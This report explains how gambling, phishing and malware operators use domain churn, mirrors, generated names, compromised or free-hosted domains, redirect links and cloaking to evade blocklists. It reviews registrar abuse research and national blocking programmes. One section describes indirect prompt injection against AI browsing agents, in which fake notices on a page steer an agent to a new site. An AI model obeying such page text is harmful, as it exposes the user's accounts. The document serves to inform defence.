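# How changing domains and mirror sites defeat blocklists, and how to protect AI browsing agents

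## Domains, blocklists and what an AI browsing agent checks

A blocklist is a list of domains or addresses that a computer may not open; it may open any others. Internet providers, companies and browser makers use blocklists to keep people away from phishing pages (imitations of a bank's or shop's site that collect passwords), malicious software and, in many countries, unlicensed gambling. When such a site is blocked, its operators register a new domain name, point it at the same server and carry on until somebody lists the new name too. This repeated replacement of names is called domain churn. A mirror site is a copy of a website at a different domain, or another address for the same service.

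A browsing agent is an AI system that opens web pages and acts on them for a user by clicking, filling in forms and signing in. Whoever deploys one has to write a navigation policy, a set of rules for which addresses the agent may open and what it may do there. These rules are hard to write mainly because some addresses are not on any list yet.

### The parts of a web address

In `https://login.example.com/account/reset`, the scheme, `https`, sets the protocol, which here is encrypted. The host name, `login.example.com`, identifies the server, and the path, `/account/reset`, identifies a page on it. Within the host name, `example.com` is the registrable domain, the part that someone can register. Its owner can put `login`, `shop` or any number of other labels in front of it for free and without anyone's permission. A site operator can therefore evade a blocklist of individual host names by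 changing the label, but has to register a new domain to evade a blocklist of registrable domains.

WHATWG's *URL*, the standard that defines how browsers read addresses, defines a registrable domain as the host's ending plus the one label before it. The ending comes from the Public Suffix List, a shared file of endings under which separate parties hold names. Counting dots is an unreliable way to find the registrable domain because the list includes both `com` and `github.io`, where each customer of a hosting service has a site. So `whatwg.github.io` is a registrable domain, and a rule that allows everything under `github.io` admits every customer of the service. WHATWG also warns against using the registrable domain as a hard security boundary, because copies of the list differ between programs.

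The same address can also be written in several ways. `EXAMPLE.COM` and `example.com` are the same host, and so are `exam%70le.org` and `example.org`. Text before an `@` is a user name, so `https://example.com@example.org` opens `example.org`. Some different names look alike because `rn` resembles `m`, or because a Latin "a" resembles a Cyrillic one. A check that compares raw text will get some of these wrong, so it should parse the address the way the browser does before comparing host names.

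### From name to page

Before a browser can fetch anything, it needs the server's numerical address. The Internet Society's *Mandated DNS Blocking* (2025) describes how the browser finds that address through the Domain Name System (DNS). The browser sends the host name, such as `example.com`, to a recursive resolver, a server that usually belongs to the user's internet provider. The resolver queries the root of the system, which returns the location of the servers for `.com`. Those servers point to the authoritative server for `example.com`, which returns the numerical address.

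The path plays no part in this. *Mandated DNS Blocking* (Gahnberg, 2026) explains to legal readers that a block at the lookup stage can cover a whole domain name but never a single page. Gahnberg writes for the Internet Society, which opposes compulsory DNS blocking, but this technical point does not depend on the policy argument.

Once the browser has the numerical address, it connects to the server, sets up encryption and sends the path. The server returns either a page or a redirect, which sends the browser to another address, and the process starts again with a new name. Checking only the address that the user or agent first chose is therefore not enough. Pages also commonly load images, video or login functions from other domains, so a very strict list can break pages on sites it allows.

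The owner of a domain can point it at a different server at any time, and can point several domains at one server. Domain churn is possible because the name and the site are separate.

### Who can act against a domain

The buyer of a domain, called the registrant, gets it from a registrar, a company that sells domain names. A registry runs the database for one domain ending, such as `.com` or `.de`. A hosting company stores the site on its servers. The registrar, registry and hosting company can act against a site in different ways, and they differ most in how narrowly they can target what they take down.

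| Party | What it can do | Smallest target | Who loses access |
|---|---|---|---|
| Registrar or registry | Suspend the domain | The registered domain and everything under it | Everyone |
| Hosting company | Remove files or close the account | One page | Everyone, at that host |
| Internet provider | Refuse the name lookup | One host name | Customers who use its resolver |
| Search engine | Drop the result | One page | Nobody, but the site is harder to find |
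| Browser | Warn or refuse before loading | One page | Users of that browser |

Registrars and registries have had a firmer duty to act since April 2024. *Compliance With DNS Abuse Obligations*, guidance from ICANN, which coordinates the domain name system, sets out the contract terms. Registrars and registries must promptly take suitable action when they have actionable evidence that a domain serves phishing, malware, botnets, pharming (hijacking lookups) or spam that delivers any of these. Gambling is not on the list, so an unlicensed casino that does none of these things seems to fall outside that duty. National endings such as `.de` have their own procedures. Registrars can still act quickly against gambling where local conditions favour it. *INFERMAL* (Nosyk, Korczyński and colleagues, 2025) cites a study of China in which most registrars suspended reported gambling and adult domains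 within 24 hours.

Two examples in the guidance show why it matters that suspension affects a whole domain. In one, a five-day-old domain shows only a fake bank login, and the registrar suspends it within two business days. In the other, the phishing page is on a franchisee's part of a car dealer's three-year-old domain, which also carries the company's email. Suspension would take down the whole site and the email, so the registrar notifies the owner instead. The first domain is maliciously registered, meaning someone bought it to abuse it. The dealer's is compromised, meaning an attacker placed content on a legitimate owner's domain.

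Internet providers block domains at the DNS lookup. Aaron (2026), in *DNS Blocking Revisited*, lists three forms of DNS blocking: the resolver replies that the domain does not exist, returns the address of another server (perhaps one that shows a notice), or does not reply. Users can avoid all three by switching to another resolver, and Aaron reports that about 21% of users worldwide already use a public one. According to TorrentFreak's *EU-Funded DNS Provider Must Block Pirate Sites, French Court Rules*, judges in Paris have since 2024 extended piracy blocking orders from internet providers to public resolvers, VPN services and search engines.

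Refusing a lookup blocks a site, which stays online but becomes unreachable for some people. In a takedown, the host removes the site or the registrar suspends the domain, so nobody can reach the site at that address. ARTICLE 19 (2026), a freedom of expression organisation that interviewed registries and registrars, points out that suspending a domain deletes nothing from the server. The operator can point a new domain at the same files or, if the host has deleted them, upload a copy elsewhere.

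### Three kinds of control and the unknown address

A blocklist lets through any new address that nobody has reported yet. An allowlist stops it, because only listed domains or addresses may be opened and everything else is refused or needs approval. A reputation system scores it using the domain's age, history, popularity, hosting or content, and somebody has to decide which score is good enough.

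Barnes, Cooper and colleagues (2016) observe in *Technical Considerations for Internet Service Blocking and Filtering* that a filter's purpose usually determines whether it blocks or allows by default. It blocks by default when the permitted activity is narrow, as on a hotel's Wi-Fi login page, and allows by default when only particular content is unwanted. They add that a blocklist needs constant maintenance, both to add entries and to remove them, because it is often hard to tell when a compromised site has been repaired and should come off the list.

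How much hangs on the default depends on how many new names there are. Slides from the internet providers' group at ICANN, ISPCP's *Emerging DNS Abuse Trends and Mitigation Strategies* (2026), put the number of newly observed domains in 2025 at 100.8 million, of which about a quarter were malicious or suspicious. That is some 276,000 new domains a day. A default of opening them lets in roughly 69,000 bad or doubtful names daily, and a default of refusing them shuts out about three unobjectionable names for every bad one. (No agent draws its addresses at random from this pool, so a quarter is not its risk per page.)

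Scoring domains is a partial solution. A newly registered domain has very little history to score, and an honest new shop has as short a history as a new phishing site. Compromised domains can be wrongly trusted because their age and clean record earn them a good score or a place on an allowlist. Nosyk and colleagues report that criminals had deliberately registered about 725,000 of the more than 1.1 million domains added to blocklists between May 2022 and April 2023. The rest, up to a third of the total, may have had records that looked fine.

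### How a browsing agent reaches a page

*The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) describes an AI agent as ordinary software built around a language model. The model plans the steps of a task and carries them out by calling tools, which either fetch information or change something. *Mind the Web* (Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues, 2025) describes how a web agent does this in a loop. The software sends the model the user's task and the current page, as code or as a screenshot. The model returns one instruction, such as clicking the "Continue" button. The software carries it out, then repeats the process with the new page.

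Addresses enter this loop from the user's request, search results, links and redirects on pages, or the model itself, which can write an address it remembers or guesses. A developer can block some of these sources. For example, the tool described in Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* accepts only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, to make it harder for the model to leak data inside an invented address. This rule does little against changing domains, because addresses in earlier search and fetch results count as having appeared, and those results can include a link to a mirror site created the day before.

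When an AI agent browses, it picks the links itself, often with nobody watching. It may also open many of them, because Anthropic sets no default limit on fetches. Suppose, for illustration, that one unfamiliar address in a hundred is harmful and that the risks are independent. A person who opens three such addresses has about a 3% chance of meeting at least one harmful page, while an agent that opens fifty has about a 39% chance (1 − 0.99^50).

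Shapira and colleagues distinguish agents by where they run, which affects whether they can reach the user's accounts. An agent installed as a browser extension works inside the user's own browser, with access to its tabs, signed-in sessions and possibly stored passwords. An agent that starts a clean browser on the user's machine has no signed-in sessions at first, but can reach local files. A remote agent on the vendor's servers starts without the user's sessions and can't reach local files, although some, such as OpenAI's Operator, could keep a login that the user had entered.

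Finally, text on a page can steer an agent. Prompt injection is text in a page or message that an AI system wrongly follows as an instruction. Kim and colleagues call it direct when the attacker's words enter through the user's input, and indirect when they wait in outside material such as a web page. In the attacks that Shapira and colleagues built, the most instructive text posed as help with the task: a fake system note recommended a visit to "our new website" for a more complete analysis. Other versions announced that the current site was out of date. A genuine service that has moved might post much the same notice, so the agent cannot dismiss every such notice as an attack. Nor does the new site have to steal a password. A browser will not send the user's bank session to a strange domain, but text on that domain could direct the agent back to the bank, where the user is already signed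 in. (This last step is an inference from the agents' access.)

### Where a check can sit

Barnes and colleagues list eight ways to stop a single page request, from preventing the lookup to preventing the server's reply. Their main objection to blocking inside the network is that the people at the ends of the connection often want to get through and find ways around the block. Someone who deploys an agent is better placed to block pages than a government, because the deployer controls one end of the connection. The agent has no motive of its own to reach a blocked site, but it may still get around a block by accident or because a page has steered it.

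A check at the DNS resolver has the broadest coverage because it applies to every program that uses the resolver, including the requests a page makes in the background, but it can use only the host name. Many organisations use protective DNS, which *Is Protective DNS Blocking the Wild West?* (2025) describes as a resolver that withholds or falsifies answers for threatening sites. A remote agent presumably uses the vendor's resolver, so neither the user's company filter nor the national block would apply to it. Aaron notes that people mistake DNS blocking for an outage. An agent could make the same mistake, search for the "missing" site and land on a mirror. Aaron's slides recommend error codes that openly identify a block, and an agent's software could treat such a code as an order to stop.

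A network proxy, a server through which the agent's traffic passes, can in principle check full addresses. But `https` encrypts the path, so the proxy can read it only by decrypting the traffic with a certificate that the agent's machine trusts. This also makes users' banking sessions readable at the proxy.

A browser can check the full address without decrypting traffic, because it has the address before the page loads and again after each redirect. Chrome and Firefox already consult Google's Safe Browsing service at this point, as Barnes and colleagues describe. The agent's own tool also has the full address, and the deployer can give it a different list for each task. But the tool can check only the requests that go through it. If the agent can also click links in a browser or run code, those requests need a separate check.

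The model can also compare the page with the task. For example, it can notice that a request to renew a library book has led to a form for card details, even if the domain is unknown to every blocklist and scoring service. But the model must read the attacker's text to make this comparison, and that text can change the result. The resolver, proxy, browser or tool code can also block a request, and that block does not depend on how the page influences the model, provided that the model cannot change the rules or use another route.

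## How operators keep a service reachable after its domain is blocked

An online casino or a phishing operation needs a domain name, a server behind it and a way for people to find it. Most blocking targets the domain name, which is usually the cheapest of these to replace. Some operators keep buying new names. Others put their pages on domains that defenders are reluctant to block, or hide the pages from whoever is checking them.

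### One service behind many names

A casino can open a mirror site without losing its customers' accounts, balances and bets, because these are stored in a database that any number of domains can use. Customers can sign in at the new domain with their old password and find the same balance. They have to enter the password again at an unfamiliar address because their old session does not carry over.

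There is little direct evidence that mirrors share accounts with the main site, even though the practice is common. The clearest source is a promotional article on the football site GHANAsoccernet, which says bettors can log in, bet and manage their balance on a mirror just as on the main site. A story carried by the radio station Three FM at least shows that a customer list can survive a closure. BloxFlip, an illegal casino for players of the game Roblox, announced in 2024 that it was shutting down permanently, but later returned under new owners. A journalist who had opened an account on the old site received a message inviting customers back.

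Some suppliers do this for many brands at once. In *Gambling is No Game*, Le Touz, Portal and colleagues (2024) traced tens of apparently unrelated betting brands to one supplier of software, hosting, payment systems and DNS settings. They call the supplier Vigorish Viper and link it to organised crime in China. It has more than 170,000 domains, which would average about 1,700 per brand even if it served a hundred brands. Infoblox, the security company they work for, has since described a second supplier with tens of thousands of domains.

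Operators with many domains can move them together using a CNAME, a DNS record that makes one name an alias of another. *Real-PGDN* (2025), a study of newly registered gambling and pornography domains, reports that many of them were aliases of a single target, so the operator could move them all by changing the target's record once. A resolver that checks the target as well as the alias can also block the whole group with one entry, but this requires care because legitimate hosting services use shared targets too.

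Mirrors defeat controls that work on one domain at a time, such as a DNS block, a registrar's suspension or an entry in a browser's list, but they do not protect anything the mirrors share. If a hosting company closes the account that holds the database, every mirror stops working until the operator restores the database elsewhere. Payment blocking also works regardless of the domain. The British Gambling Commission's *Illegal online gambling* (2025) describes how officials make a test deposit on an unlicensed site and send the evidence to Visa, which traces the bank that processes the site's card payments. That bank then has to drop the site as a customer. A new domain would not by itself restore card payments, although a second merchant account might.

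Blocking a server's numerical address can stop several scam sites at once, but it can also block legitimate sites that share the address. *Anansi* (2026), a study of job scams that reach people by message, found that 135 scam websites led to 80 addresses. Twelve of the sites shared one address in Japan, so a single blocklist entry would have stopped all twelve. However, about 45% of the sites were on Cloudflare's network, whose addresses also serve many legitimate sites.

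### Where the names come from

Malwarebytes' *The dark side of sports betting* (2025) attributes over 100 domains to the brand 20Bet and over 40 to MostBet. The bare name `20bet` appears under 18 endings, from `.asia` to `.win`, and other domains add a country or a word, as in `20betbrasil` and `20betlogin`. MostBet's names include a numbered series from `mostbet-in33` to `mostbet-in62`, with gaps. Fourteen more are strings of letters and digits that end in `mb`, and some contain nothing recognisable.

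Some of these sites may not belong to the casinos, so a familiar logo is poor evidence of who runs a page. Malwarebytes notes that many such sites exist to earn commission by referring customers, and some copies exist to steal money or personal details.

The same patterns appear in blocking orders. SoloAzar's *Ukraine Blocks 475 Illegal Gambling Websites as Mirror Networks Expand* (2026) reports that 268 of the 475 domains combined the brand GetX with words such as "casino", "vip" and "zerkalo", which is Russian for "mirror". More than 150 others looked random. The gambling analytics firm Blask reports that Belgian authorities blacklisted `bcgame.com` in November 2024 and in May 2026 were blocking variants of the same brand name that used `.nl`, added "belgium" or added a zero.

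A rule that matches text can catch the branded names. For example, blocking every domain that contains `getx` will stop much of that series before a regulator has listed it, but it will also block any news site or support group with the word in its domain. Such a rule can't catch random names, but customers can't recognise or remember them either, so an operator who uses them depends more heavily on links.

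Operators can afford all these names because registrars sell them cheaply and in bulk. Interisle (2026), a consultancy that studies domain abuse, counted 84,961,989 domains created in 2025 under generic endings such as `.com` and `.top`. By 18 May 2026, security companies had put 8,496,811 of them (10%) on blocklists, or about 23,000 for every day of 2025. Interisle judges that criminals had bought about 98% of the blocklisted domains to abuse them.

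Interisle thinks the share of new domains that criminals bought may be closer to 20%. It expects later listings to bring the total to about 10.1 million, partly because some criminals leave domains unused for months so that they no longer look new. It then adds two-thirds, for a total of 16.8 million, because ICANN researchers found that for every three blocklisted domains, two unlisted ones appeared to come from the same registration batches. This last step assumes that the unlisted domains in a batch are bad too, which is plausible but not certain. If they are, blocklists miss two in every five domains that criminals buy. The registrar is better able to find them, because it can look up what else the buyer of a bad domain has bought.

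Blocking an entire top-level domain would be a blunt response to bulk registration. In Interisle's data, about 35% of new `.top` domains were malicious, so blocking `.top` would also block the other 65%. The `.com` domain had the most malicious registrations, 1.9 million, but these were only 4.9% of its new registrations.

Phishing accounts for part of this demand. The *Phishing Activity Trends Report, 2nd Quarter 2026* (2026) from APWG, an industry group that collects phishing reports, counts 1,069,681 phishing sites in the quarter. June had 425,808, the most in any month since April 2023. One domain can hold several of these sites. Interisle's *Phishing Landscape 2025* (2025) reports over 1.5 million domains used for phishing in its study year. Phishers had acquired 37% of them through bulk registration services.

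### What attracts phishers to a registrar

Phishers favour some registrars and domain endings over others. Nosyk and colleagues tried to find out why in *INFERMAL*, a study that KOR Labs and Université Grenoble Alpes carried out with ICANN. They started with reports of 534,000 phishing addresses on 108,000 domains, collected between August 2023 and January 2024. To exclude compromised domains, they kept only those registered within the 90 days before blocklisting and suspended by a registrar or registry within a month after it. That left about 28,000 domains, and the researchers had price and policy data for 14,474 of them, from 31 registrars.

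Researchers used 73 features to describe what registrars offered, including prices, payment methods and identity checks, and tested some of these by shopping for domains. At each registrar, they tried to add three domain names to the basket: a random string, `office365-my-account` and `facebook-login-page`. Two registrars refused the branded names, while all accepted the random one. Another registrar automatically generated a note recommending `facebook-login-page.company` for a site with a "secure and official login page for Facebook users". Nearly half of the malicious domains in the sample had cost $2 or less.

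The main regression used 1,066 pairs of registrar and domain ending, such as NameSilo and `.top`, and related the number of malicious domains in each pair to 14 features. A second regression compared individual malicious domains with about 15,400 ordinary ones.

| Feature | Change in number of malicious domains per pair | Change in odds that a domain is malicious |
|---|---|---|
| Each extra dollar of discount | +49% | +1.3% |
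| Each dollar off the registration price | +6.6% | Not significant |
| Registration or account creation by API (software can place the orders) | +401% | Not significant |
| Free web hosting | +88% | Not significant |
| Payment by cryptocurrency | +30% | Not significant |
| Payment by bank transfer | −74% | Not significant |
| Email or phone check before purchase | −70% | Not significant |
| Restrictions on who may register | −63% | −19% |
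| Free encryption certificate | −81% | Not significant |
| Longer time until suspension | Close to zero | Not significant |

The 49% increase in abuse is for each dollar of advertised discount, while a dollar off the price itself was associated with only 6.6% more abuse. The study's abstract and Interisle both apply the larger figure to price reductions in general. That rate also can't hold over the whole range of the data, because compounded over the largest discount in the sample, $12.95, it would mean more than 170 times as many malicious domains.

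All of these figures are associations. Registrars choose their own prices and rules, and a registrar with an API may differ from one without it in many other ways, such as size. The 14 features in the main regression do not include total sales, so anything that makes a registrar popular with all buyers can raise its count of malicious domains. In the second regression, which compares malicious buyers with ordinary ones, the API is no longer significant, and only discounts and restrictions are. The certificate result also calls for caution, since it is hard to see why a free certificate would deter phishers, and only 235 of the domains came with that offer.

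There is somewhat better evidence on price from an earlier study of the Chinese ending `.cn`, which Nosyk and colleagues cite. When the registry raised its minimum price from at most 15 cents to $10 and asked buyers for more documents, spammers switched to other endings. That suggests that cost and paperwork do drive abusers away, but also that they go somewhere else while cheap names remain on sale. (The registry made both changes, so the study can't separate them.)

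The researchers found almost no relation between takedown speed and abuse. They explain this by saying that even a short-lived phishing site can collect valuable passwords. That may be true, but their sample could hardly have shown a relation, because it excluded domains that weren't suspended within a month. The domains it included lasted on average about an hour after blocklisting, and at most 18 hours. In Interisle's case studies of large criminal campaigns, registrars and registries had suspended only small percentages of the blocklisted domains. It is still unclear whether slow registrars attract more abuse than fast ones.

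### Names that software computes

Malware has to contact its operator for instructions. If it always uses the same domain, defenders can block that domain. Many malware authors therefore build in a domain generation algorithm, a calculation that turns the date into a list of domain names. The operator runs the same calculation, registers one of the names and waits for the infected computers to try it.

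The best-known example is Conficker, a worm that began spreading among Windows computers in November 2008. Each of its first two versions computed 250 domain names a day, so a blocklist would have needed 91,250 names a year for each version. A later version computed 50,000 a day, or 18.25 million a year, and every infected computer tried 500 of them each day. Defenders had to block all 50,000 names each day to shut the operators out, because the operators needed only one, which about 1% of the infected computers (500 out of 50,000) would try that day.

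But anyone who knows the algorithm can compute the names in advance. Researchers reverse-engineered Conficker to do this, and a group of security companies, registries and ICANN used the results to block or register names before the operators could. A list compiled from abuse reports would always have been too late. The work was laborious because the later version spread its names over more than a hundred top-level domains, and the group had to persuade the registries that ran them to cooperate. Some of the computed names also belonged to unrelated websites already. Defenders can compute names only as far ahead as they know the algorithm's inputs, so an algorithm that also uses that day's exchange rates, for example, leaves them a few hours.

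Casinos and phishers can't use this method because they need to reach people, who don't compute domain names. Some of them instead run a program themselves to generate many names, then register them all. Defenders never get a copy of that program, so they have to guess the pattern from names that have already appeared. MostBet's strings ending in `mb` look like the output of such a program, though a list of names can't prove it.

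Fast flux, which people sometimes confuse with domain churn, keeps the same domain name but changes the servers behind it. The operator's DNS servers return a constantly changing set of IP addresses, often those of hacked home computers that pass the traffic on to a hidden server, and resolvers have to request the addresses again every few minutes. A list of IP addresses therefore goes out of date almost at once, but blocking or suspending the domain still works. With domain churn, the servers may well stay where they are while the name changes, so a list of IP addresses may keep working after a domain blocklist goes out of date.

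*Real-PGDN* reports that gambling and pornography domains move back and forth between a small number of IP addresses. If an operator also switches to new domain names, neither a domain blocklist nor an IP blocklist works for long on its own.

### Pages on other people's domains

An operator can also use a domain that belongs to somebody else. In *Phishing Landscape 2026*, Strutt and Piscitello (2026) estimate that phishers themselves registered about three-quarters of phishing domains in recent years, and they count the rest as compromised. One example in *INFERMAL* is a fake bill from the telecommunications company Swisscom on a British website whose domain dated from 2008.

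Zagi, Digdo and Shalannanda (2025), in *Just Dork and Crawl*, measured the practice for gambling in Indonesia, where gambling is illegal. From 27 May to 25 June 2025 they repeatedly searched sites under `.id` for nine words typical of gambling advertisements, such as "slot" and "togel" (a lottery game), and had a crawler revisit the results. They found 453 suspicious pages and confirmed gambling content on 346 of them, across 147 websites. Most of the false alarms came from the word "bet", which also appears in "between". Academic institutions owned 65 of the websites, and government bodies owned 39.

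Visitors to these sites often saw nothing unusual. On 51.7% of the pages, the attackers had put gambling text and links in the page's code with an instruction not to display them, and on 22.8% they had placed them far outside the visible screen. The purpose is to influence search engines, which read the code and find what looks like a university linking to a casino. (A browsing agent that reads the code of a page instead of a screenshot would presumably read this text too. That is an inference, since the study did not test agents.)

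The gambling content took a mean of 75.3 hours to disappear, with a median of 47.4 hours, when averaged over repeated incidents on the same page. After the first incident, the median was 32.7 hours, and 43% of the pages were clean within a day. The content came back on 150 of the 346 pages, and one page went through 112 rounds. Zagi and colleagues could not always distinguish a repair from an outage, because a page that their crawler failed to reach also counted as free of gambling words. They could also find a page only after a search engine had indexed it, so visitors had probably been exposed for longer than these times suggest.

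Free hosting gives an operator much the same advantage without a break-in. Phishers open an account with a hosting service and get an address under the service's own domain. *INFERMAL* also describes an example of this, a fake AT&T login at `attsecure0.weebly.com`. Strutt and Piscitello point out that companies tend to trust everything under hosting domains such as `pages.dev` and `windows.net`. Some of these services also offer AI tools that phishers can use to closely copy a brand's page, with a working login form.

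Pages on borrowed domains get past reputation scores and allowlists that apply to the whole domain, and registrars usually will not suspend the domain. Browser blocklists work if they list the exact page, and so does reporting the page to the domain's owner or the hosting company.

Some phishers also evade blocklist entries for exact addresses. *An Analysis of Architectural and Operational Dynamics of Phishkits in the Wild* (2026) examines ready-made packages of files for phishing sites. Of these, 140 (10.7%) copied the whole site to a randomly named path and sent visitors there. Blocking the whole domain defeats this, so the trick is more useful on a domain that defenders don't want to block, such as that of a hospital or a large hosting service.

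### Links that stay while the address changes

A new domain is of little use if customers don't know about it. Operators therefore give customers an address that stays the same, and only have to change where it leads when the current domain stops working. This address may be a short link, a page on a link-listing service or a page planted on a hacked website.

The Indonesian study found signs of this. Gambling links on 16 domains went through the link service `heylink.me`, and Zagi and colleagues suggest that the attackers used it to manage and hide their destinations. Another 28 pages on 13 websites forwarded visitors automatically, and six of these websites led to more than one gambling domain during the month. On one of the six, three pages switched to the same new destination each time, so someone was probably controlling them together.

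Customers can also find a blocked service by searching for its brand name. The Gambling Commission gets search companies to remove illegal sites from their British results, but acknowledges that the sites often reappear.

Such links get past a filter that checks only the first address, but not one that checks the whole chain. Blocking the stable link can be more effective than blocking any of the destinations, because customers who rely on that link then can't find the next destination. But the link is often on a service with many legitimate users, so the block has to name the exact page.

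Following a link may reveal few of its destinations. One job-scam domain in *Anansi* first displayed a maintenance notice, then redirected the visitor to a working scam site when the page was reloaded. Repeated automated visits led to a different site each time. A scanner that visited only once might have recorded a broken page, and would have learned one address at most.

### Different pages for different visitors

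Cloaking means showing harmless content to security scanners and the real content to intended victims. The server chooses which to show based on what it can observe about each visitor. *Phishkits in the Wild* describes a phishing kit that looked up the country of each visitor's IP address, let in visitors from South Africa, and sent everyone else to another banking login page.

Vigorish Viper's checks are more elaborate. Le Touz and colleagues describe several layers of DNS aliases and page scripts that a visitor has to pass through. The scripts check the visitor's IP address and keep monitoring mouse movements. Some other illegal gambling sites change their display depending on the visitor's device, according to an official quoted in Focus Gaming News' *British Gambling Commission adapts to illegal market’s “unusual advertising methods”*.

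Cloaking mainly works against the people and programs that compile blocklists. A scanner in a data centre receives a harmless page and does not list the site, and a hosting company that follows up a complaint may see the same page and close the case. Reputation systems that score content have this problem too. Cloaking does not remove a domain that is already on a user's blocklist, or get around an allowlist that omits it. A check in the victim's browser is also harder to fool, because it examines the page the victim received. Investigators can get closer to seeing that page by looking like customers. When the Gambling Commission makes test purchases, it visits from a British address and records this as evidence.

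The page a browsing agent receives probably depends on where the agent runs. An agent in the user's own browser has the user's IP address and device, so a cloaked site may show it the harmful page hidden from scanners. A remote agent on a vendor's servers looks more like a scanner and may get the harmless version. But a remote agent could also open sites that the user's own browser can't. The Gambling Commission asks unlicensed casinos to shut out British visitors, and some comply by blocking British IP addresses. An agent running on a server abroad could still open such a casino for a user in Britain. These are inferences from how cloaking and location blocking work, and none of the studies above tested them on agents.

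## What national blocking of gambling sites has achieved

Regulators in several countries publish how many illegal gambling sites they have acted against, and some name every site. These records are useful to anyone planning a blocklist because gambling operators keep changing domains. The records concern people using browsers, so any conclusion about AI agents drawn from them is an inference.

### Four national programmes

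Australia relies mainly on its internet providers to block gambling sites. The Australian Communications and Media Authority (ACMA) investigates complaints about gambling services, warns operators that break the law and asks providers to block their sites. It makes these requests under section 313 of the Telecommunications Act 1997, according to Winston's *The ACMA blocks 8 new illegal online gambling websites* (2026). ACMA made its first request in November 2019. The total number of blocked sites was 1,564 in March 2026 and had reached 1,774 by July, according to ACMA's *Latest illegal online gambling websites blocked* (2026). The total includes affiliate sites, which advertise casinos.

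The British Gambling Commission first gives the operator of an unlicensed site 48 hours to block British visitors, down from 14 days. The Commission says its officials then write to the site's registrar and hosting company, which may suspend the site for 90 days or longer, depending on their own policies. Whether or not those companies act, officials send all the site's addresses to Google and Bing for removal from British search results, and later check whether the site has come back.

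None of these steps involves the visitor's internet provider or compels a registrar to act. Since 30 November 2026, however, the Commission's officers have been able to obtain court orders to suspend domains and IP addresses, as Tupikova (2026) reports in *Gambling Commission Domain and IP Suspension Powers Take Effect*. The power is too new to have produced results.

Norway has allowed DNS blocking of gambling sites since 1 January 2025. The Norwegian Gambling Authority (Lotteritilsynet) has ordered internet providers to block 238 sites: 57 in March 2025, 47 in June 2025 and 134 in February 2026. Anyone who tries to open one sees a page from their provider explaining the block. The regulator lists only sites that target Norway. Signs of this include using Norwegian, accepting kroner and filling in the +47 dialling code when a customer registers, so a company that wants to leave the market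 has to do more than switch its site to English.

Ukraine acts in large batches, such as its August 2026 order against 475 sites.

### Pages, domains and brands

Halvorsen (2026), in *UKGC*, put the British total at 7.8 million illegal gambling URLs in six months of 2026, compared with 117,711 in the quarter from July to September 2025. A URL is the address of a single page, and one casino can have thousands of pages, so the number of URLs can rise much faster than the number of gambling sites. The Gambling Commission's *Activity to tackle unlicensed gambling and outcomes* counts websites separately from URLs and shows a much smaller rise in websites.

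| Quarter | URLs sent to search engines | Websites sent to search engines | URLs per website | Referrals to registrars or hosts | Sites they removed or suspended |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Apr–Jun 2025 | 32,608 | 321 | 102 | 147 | 22 |
| Jul–Sep 2025 | 117,711 | 272 | 433 | 144 | 20 |
| Oct–Dec 2025 | 117,645 | 123 | 956 | 85 | 8 |
| Jan–Mar 2026 | 70,308 | 226 | 311 | 66 | 3 |
| Apr–Jun 2026 | 147,721 | 366 | 404 | 103 | 14 |
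| Jul–Sep 2026 | 7,677,211 | 1,835 | 4,184 | 373 | 7 |

Between the third quarter of 2025 and the third quarter of 2026, the number of URLs grew 65-fold and the number of websites almost sevenfold. About 98% of the 7.8 million URLs came from the last quarter. The Commission does not explain why the average site had ten times as many pages. Officials may have started collecting addresses more thoroughly, or a few sites may have generated huge numbers of pages. One brand can run dozens of sites, so the number of websites is also not a reliable measure of the number of casinos.

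Australia's total counts domain names. It rose by 187, from 1,564 in March 2026 to 1,751 in June, and ACMA's *Action on interactive gambling and gambling advertising* (2026) lists 187 names for April to June. ACMA notes that these include alternate sites set up to evade earlier blocks. The string `wonaco` appears in 21 of the 187 names, from `wonaco.com` to `wonaco-8844.com`, so one brand accounts for about one in nine of the quarter's blocks.

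The number of blocks can therefore rise even if the number of casinos does not. According to ACMA's *Action on interactive gambling* (2025), the regulator completed 29 investigations and referred 71 sites for blocking in July to September 2025. In April to June 2026, it completed 30 investigations and referred 187 sites. By then ACMA had decided to go after sites that get around its blocks, which probably explains part of the increase.

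Norway's February 2026 order, by contrast, generally lists one domain for each brand, and for Wonaco it lists only `wonaco3.com`. Norway's 134 blocks probably cover more brands than Australia's 187, so the totals are a poor guide to how many casinos each regulator has dealt with.

### Three months' notice

Lotteritilsynet's *Vedtak med pålegg om DNS-blokkering av nettsteder som tilbyr pengespill uten tillatelse* (2026) describes how Norway adds sites to its blocklist. Officials began collecting evidence on 4 July 2025. They sent providers an advance notice on 24 November, took comments until 16 December, checked the sites again and issued the order on 19 February 2026. Providers had until 26 February to comply, 94 days after the notice and almost eight months after officials began collecting evidence.

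The operators also received a copy of the notice, so they had three months to prepare a replacement domain. Norwegian law makes this advance warning hard to avoid. The regulator has to try to contact the operator before ordering a block, and must also weigh the block against freedom of information and the interests of the companies involved.

The notice also has benefits. Of the 178 sites it covered, 44 were no longer on the list in February. Many operators had complied, for example by shutting out Norwegian players, and a few were still in talks with the regulator. With a faster procedure, the regulator might have blocked those 44 sites unnecessarily or missed a chance to persuade their owners to leave.

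The order has no rule for mirrors and requires providers to block only the listed names. About 60 of the 134 names end in a number, so their successors are easy to guess, but a successor such as `wonaco4.com` would apparently need its own assessment, notice and order. One entry, `no.miki.com`, is a subdomain of a domain that the order does not block, so its operator could escape the block by changing the first label.

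In May 2025, less than two months after the first blocking order, Norway's regulator gave notice of a second round, covering 62 more sites that belonged to the same companies. Some of these may have been mirrors that replaced the blocked sites, but they may also have been other brands that the companies already owned.

The government's 2026 consultation leaves this gap open. In *Forslag til endringer i forskrift 17. november 2022 nr. 1978 om pengespill* (2026), the Ministry of Culture and Equality proposes rules for the page that blocked visitors see, the personal data that providers may keep, and a public list with the reason for each block. The ministry describes these as clarifications that leave the substance of the law unchanged, and does not mention mirrors when explaining them.

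Lotteritilsynet also has no power to block a site that only advertises gambling, so it presumably cannot block a page that just lists a casino's current address. In Australia, ACMA can block affiliate sites, which include at least some of these pages.

### Does blocking reduce illegal gambling?

When the Norwegian government proposed DNS blocking, it accepted that people could get around it. It argued, as reported in Digi.no's *Regjeringen foreslår å blokkere ulovlige spill-nettsteder*, that having to take an active step to do so would raise the threshold for visiting an unlicensed site. This is plausible for someone who taps on an advertisement out of curiosity, but less so for a regular customer with money in an account, because the casino can email them a new link.

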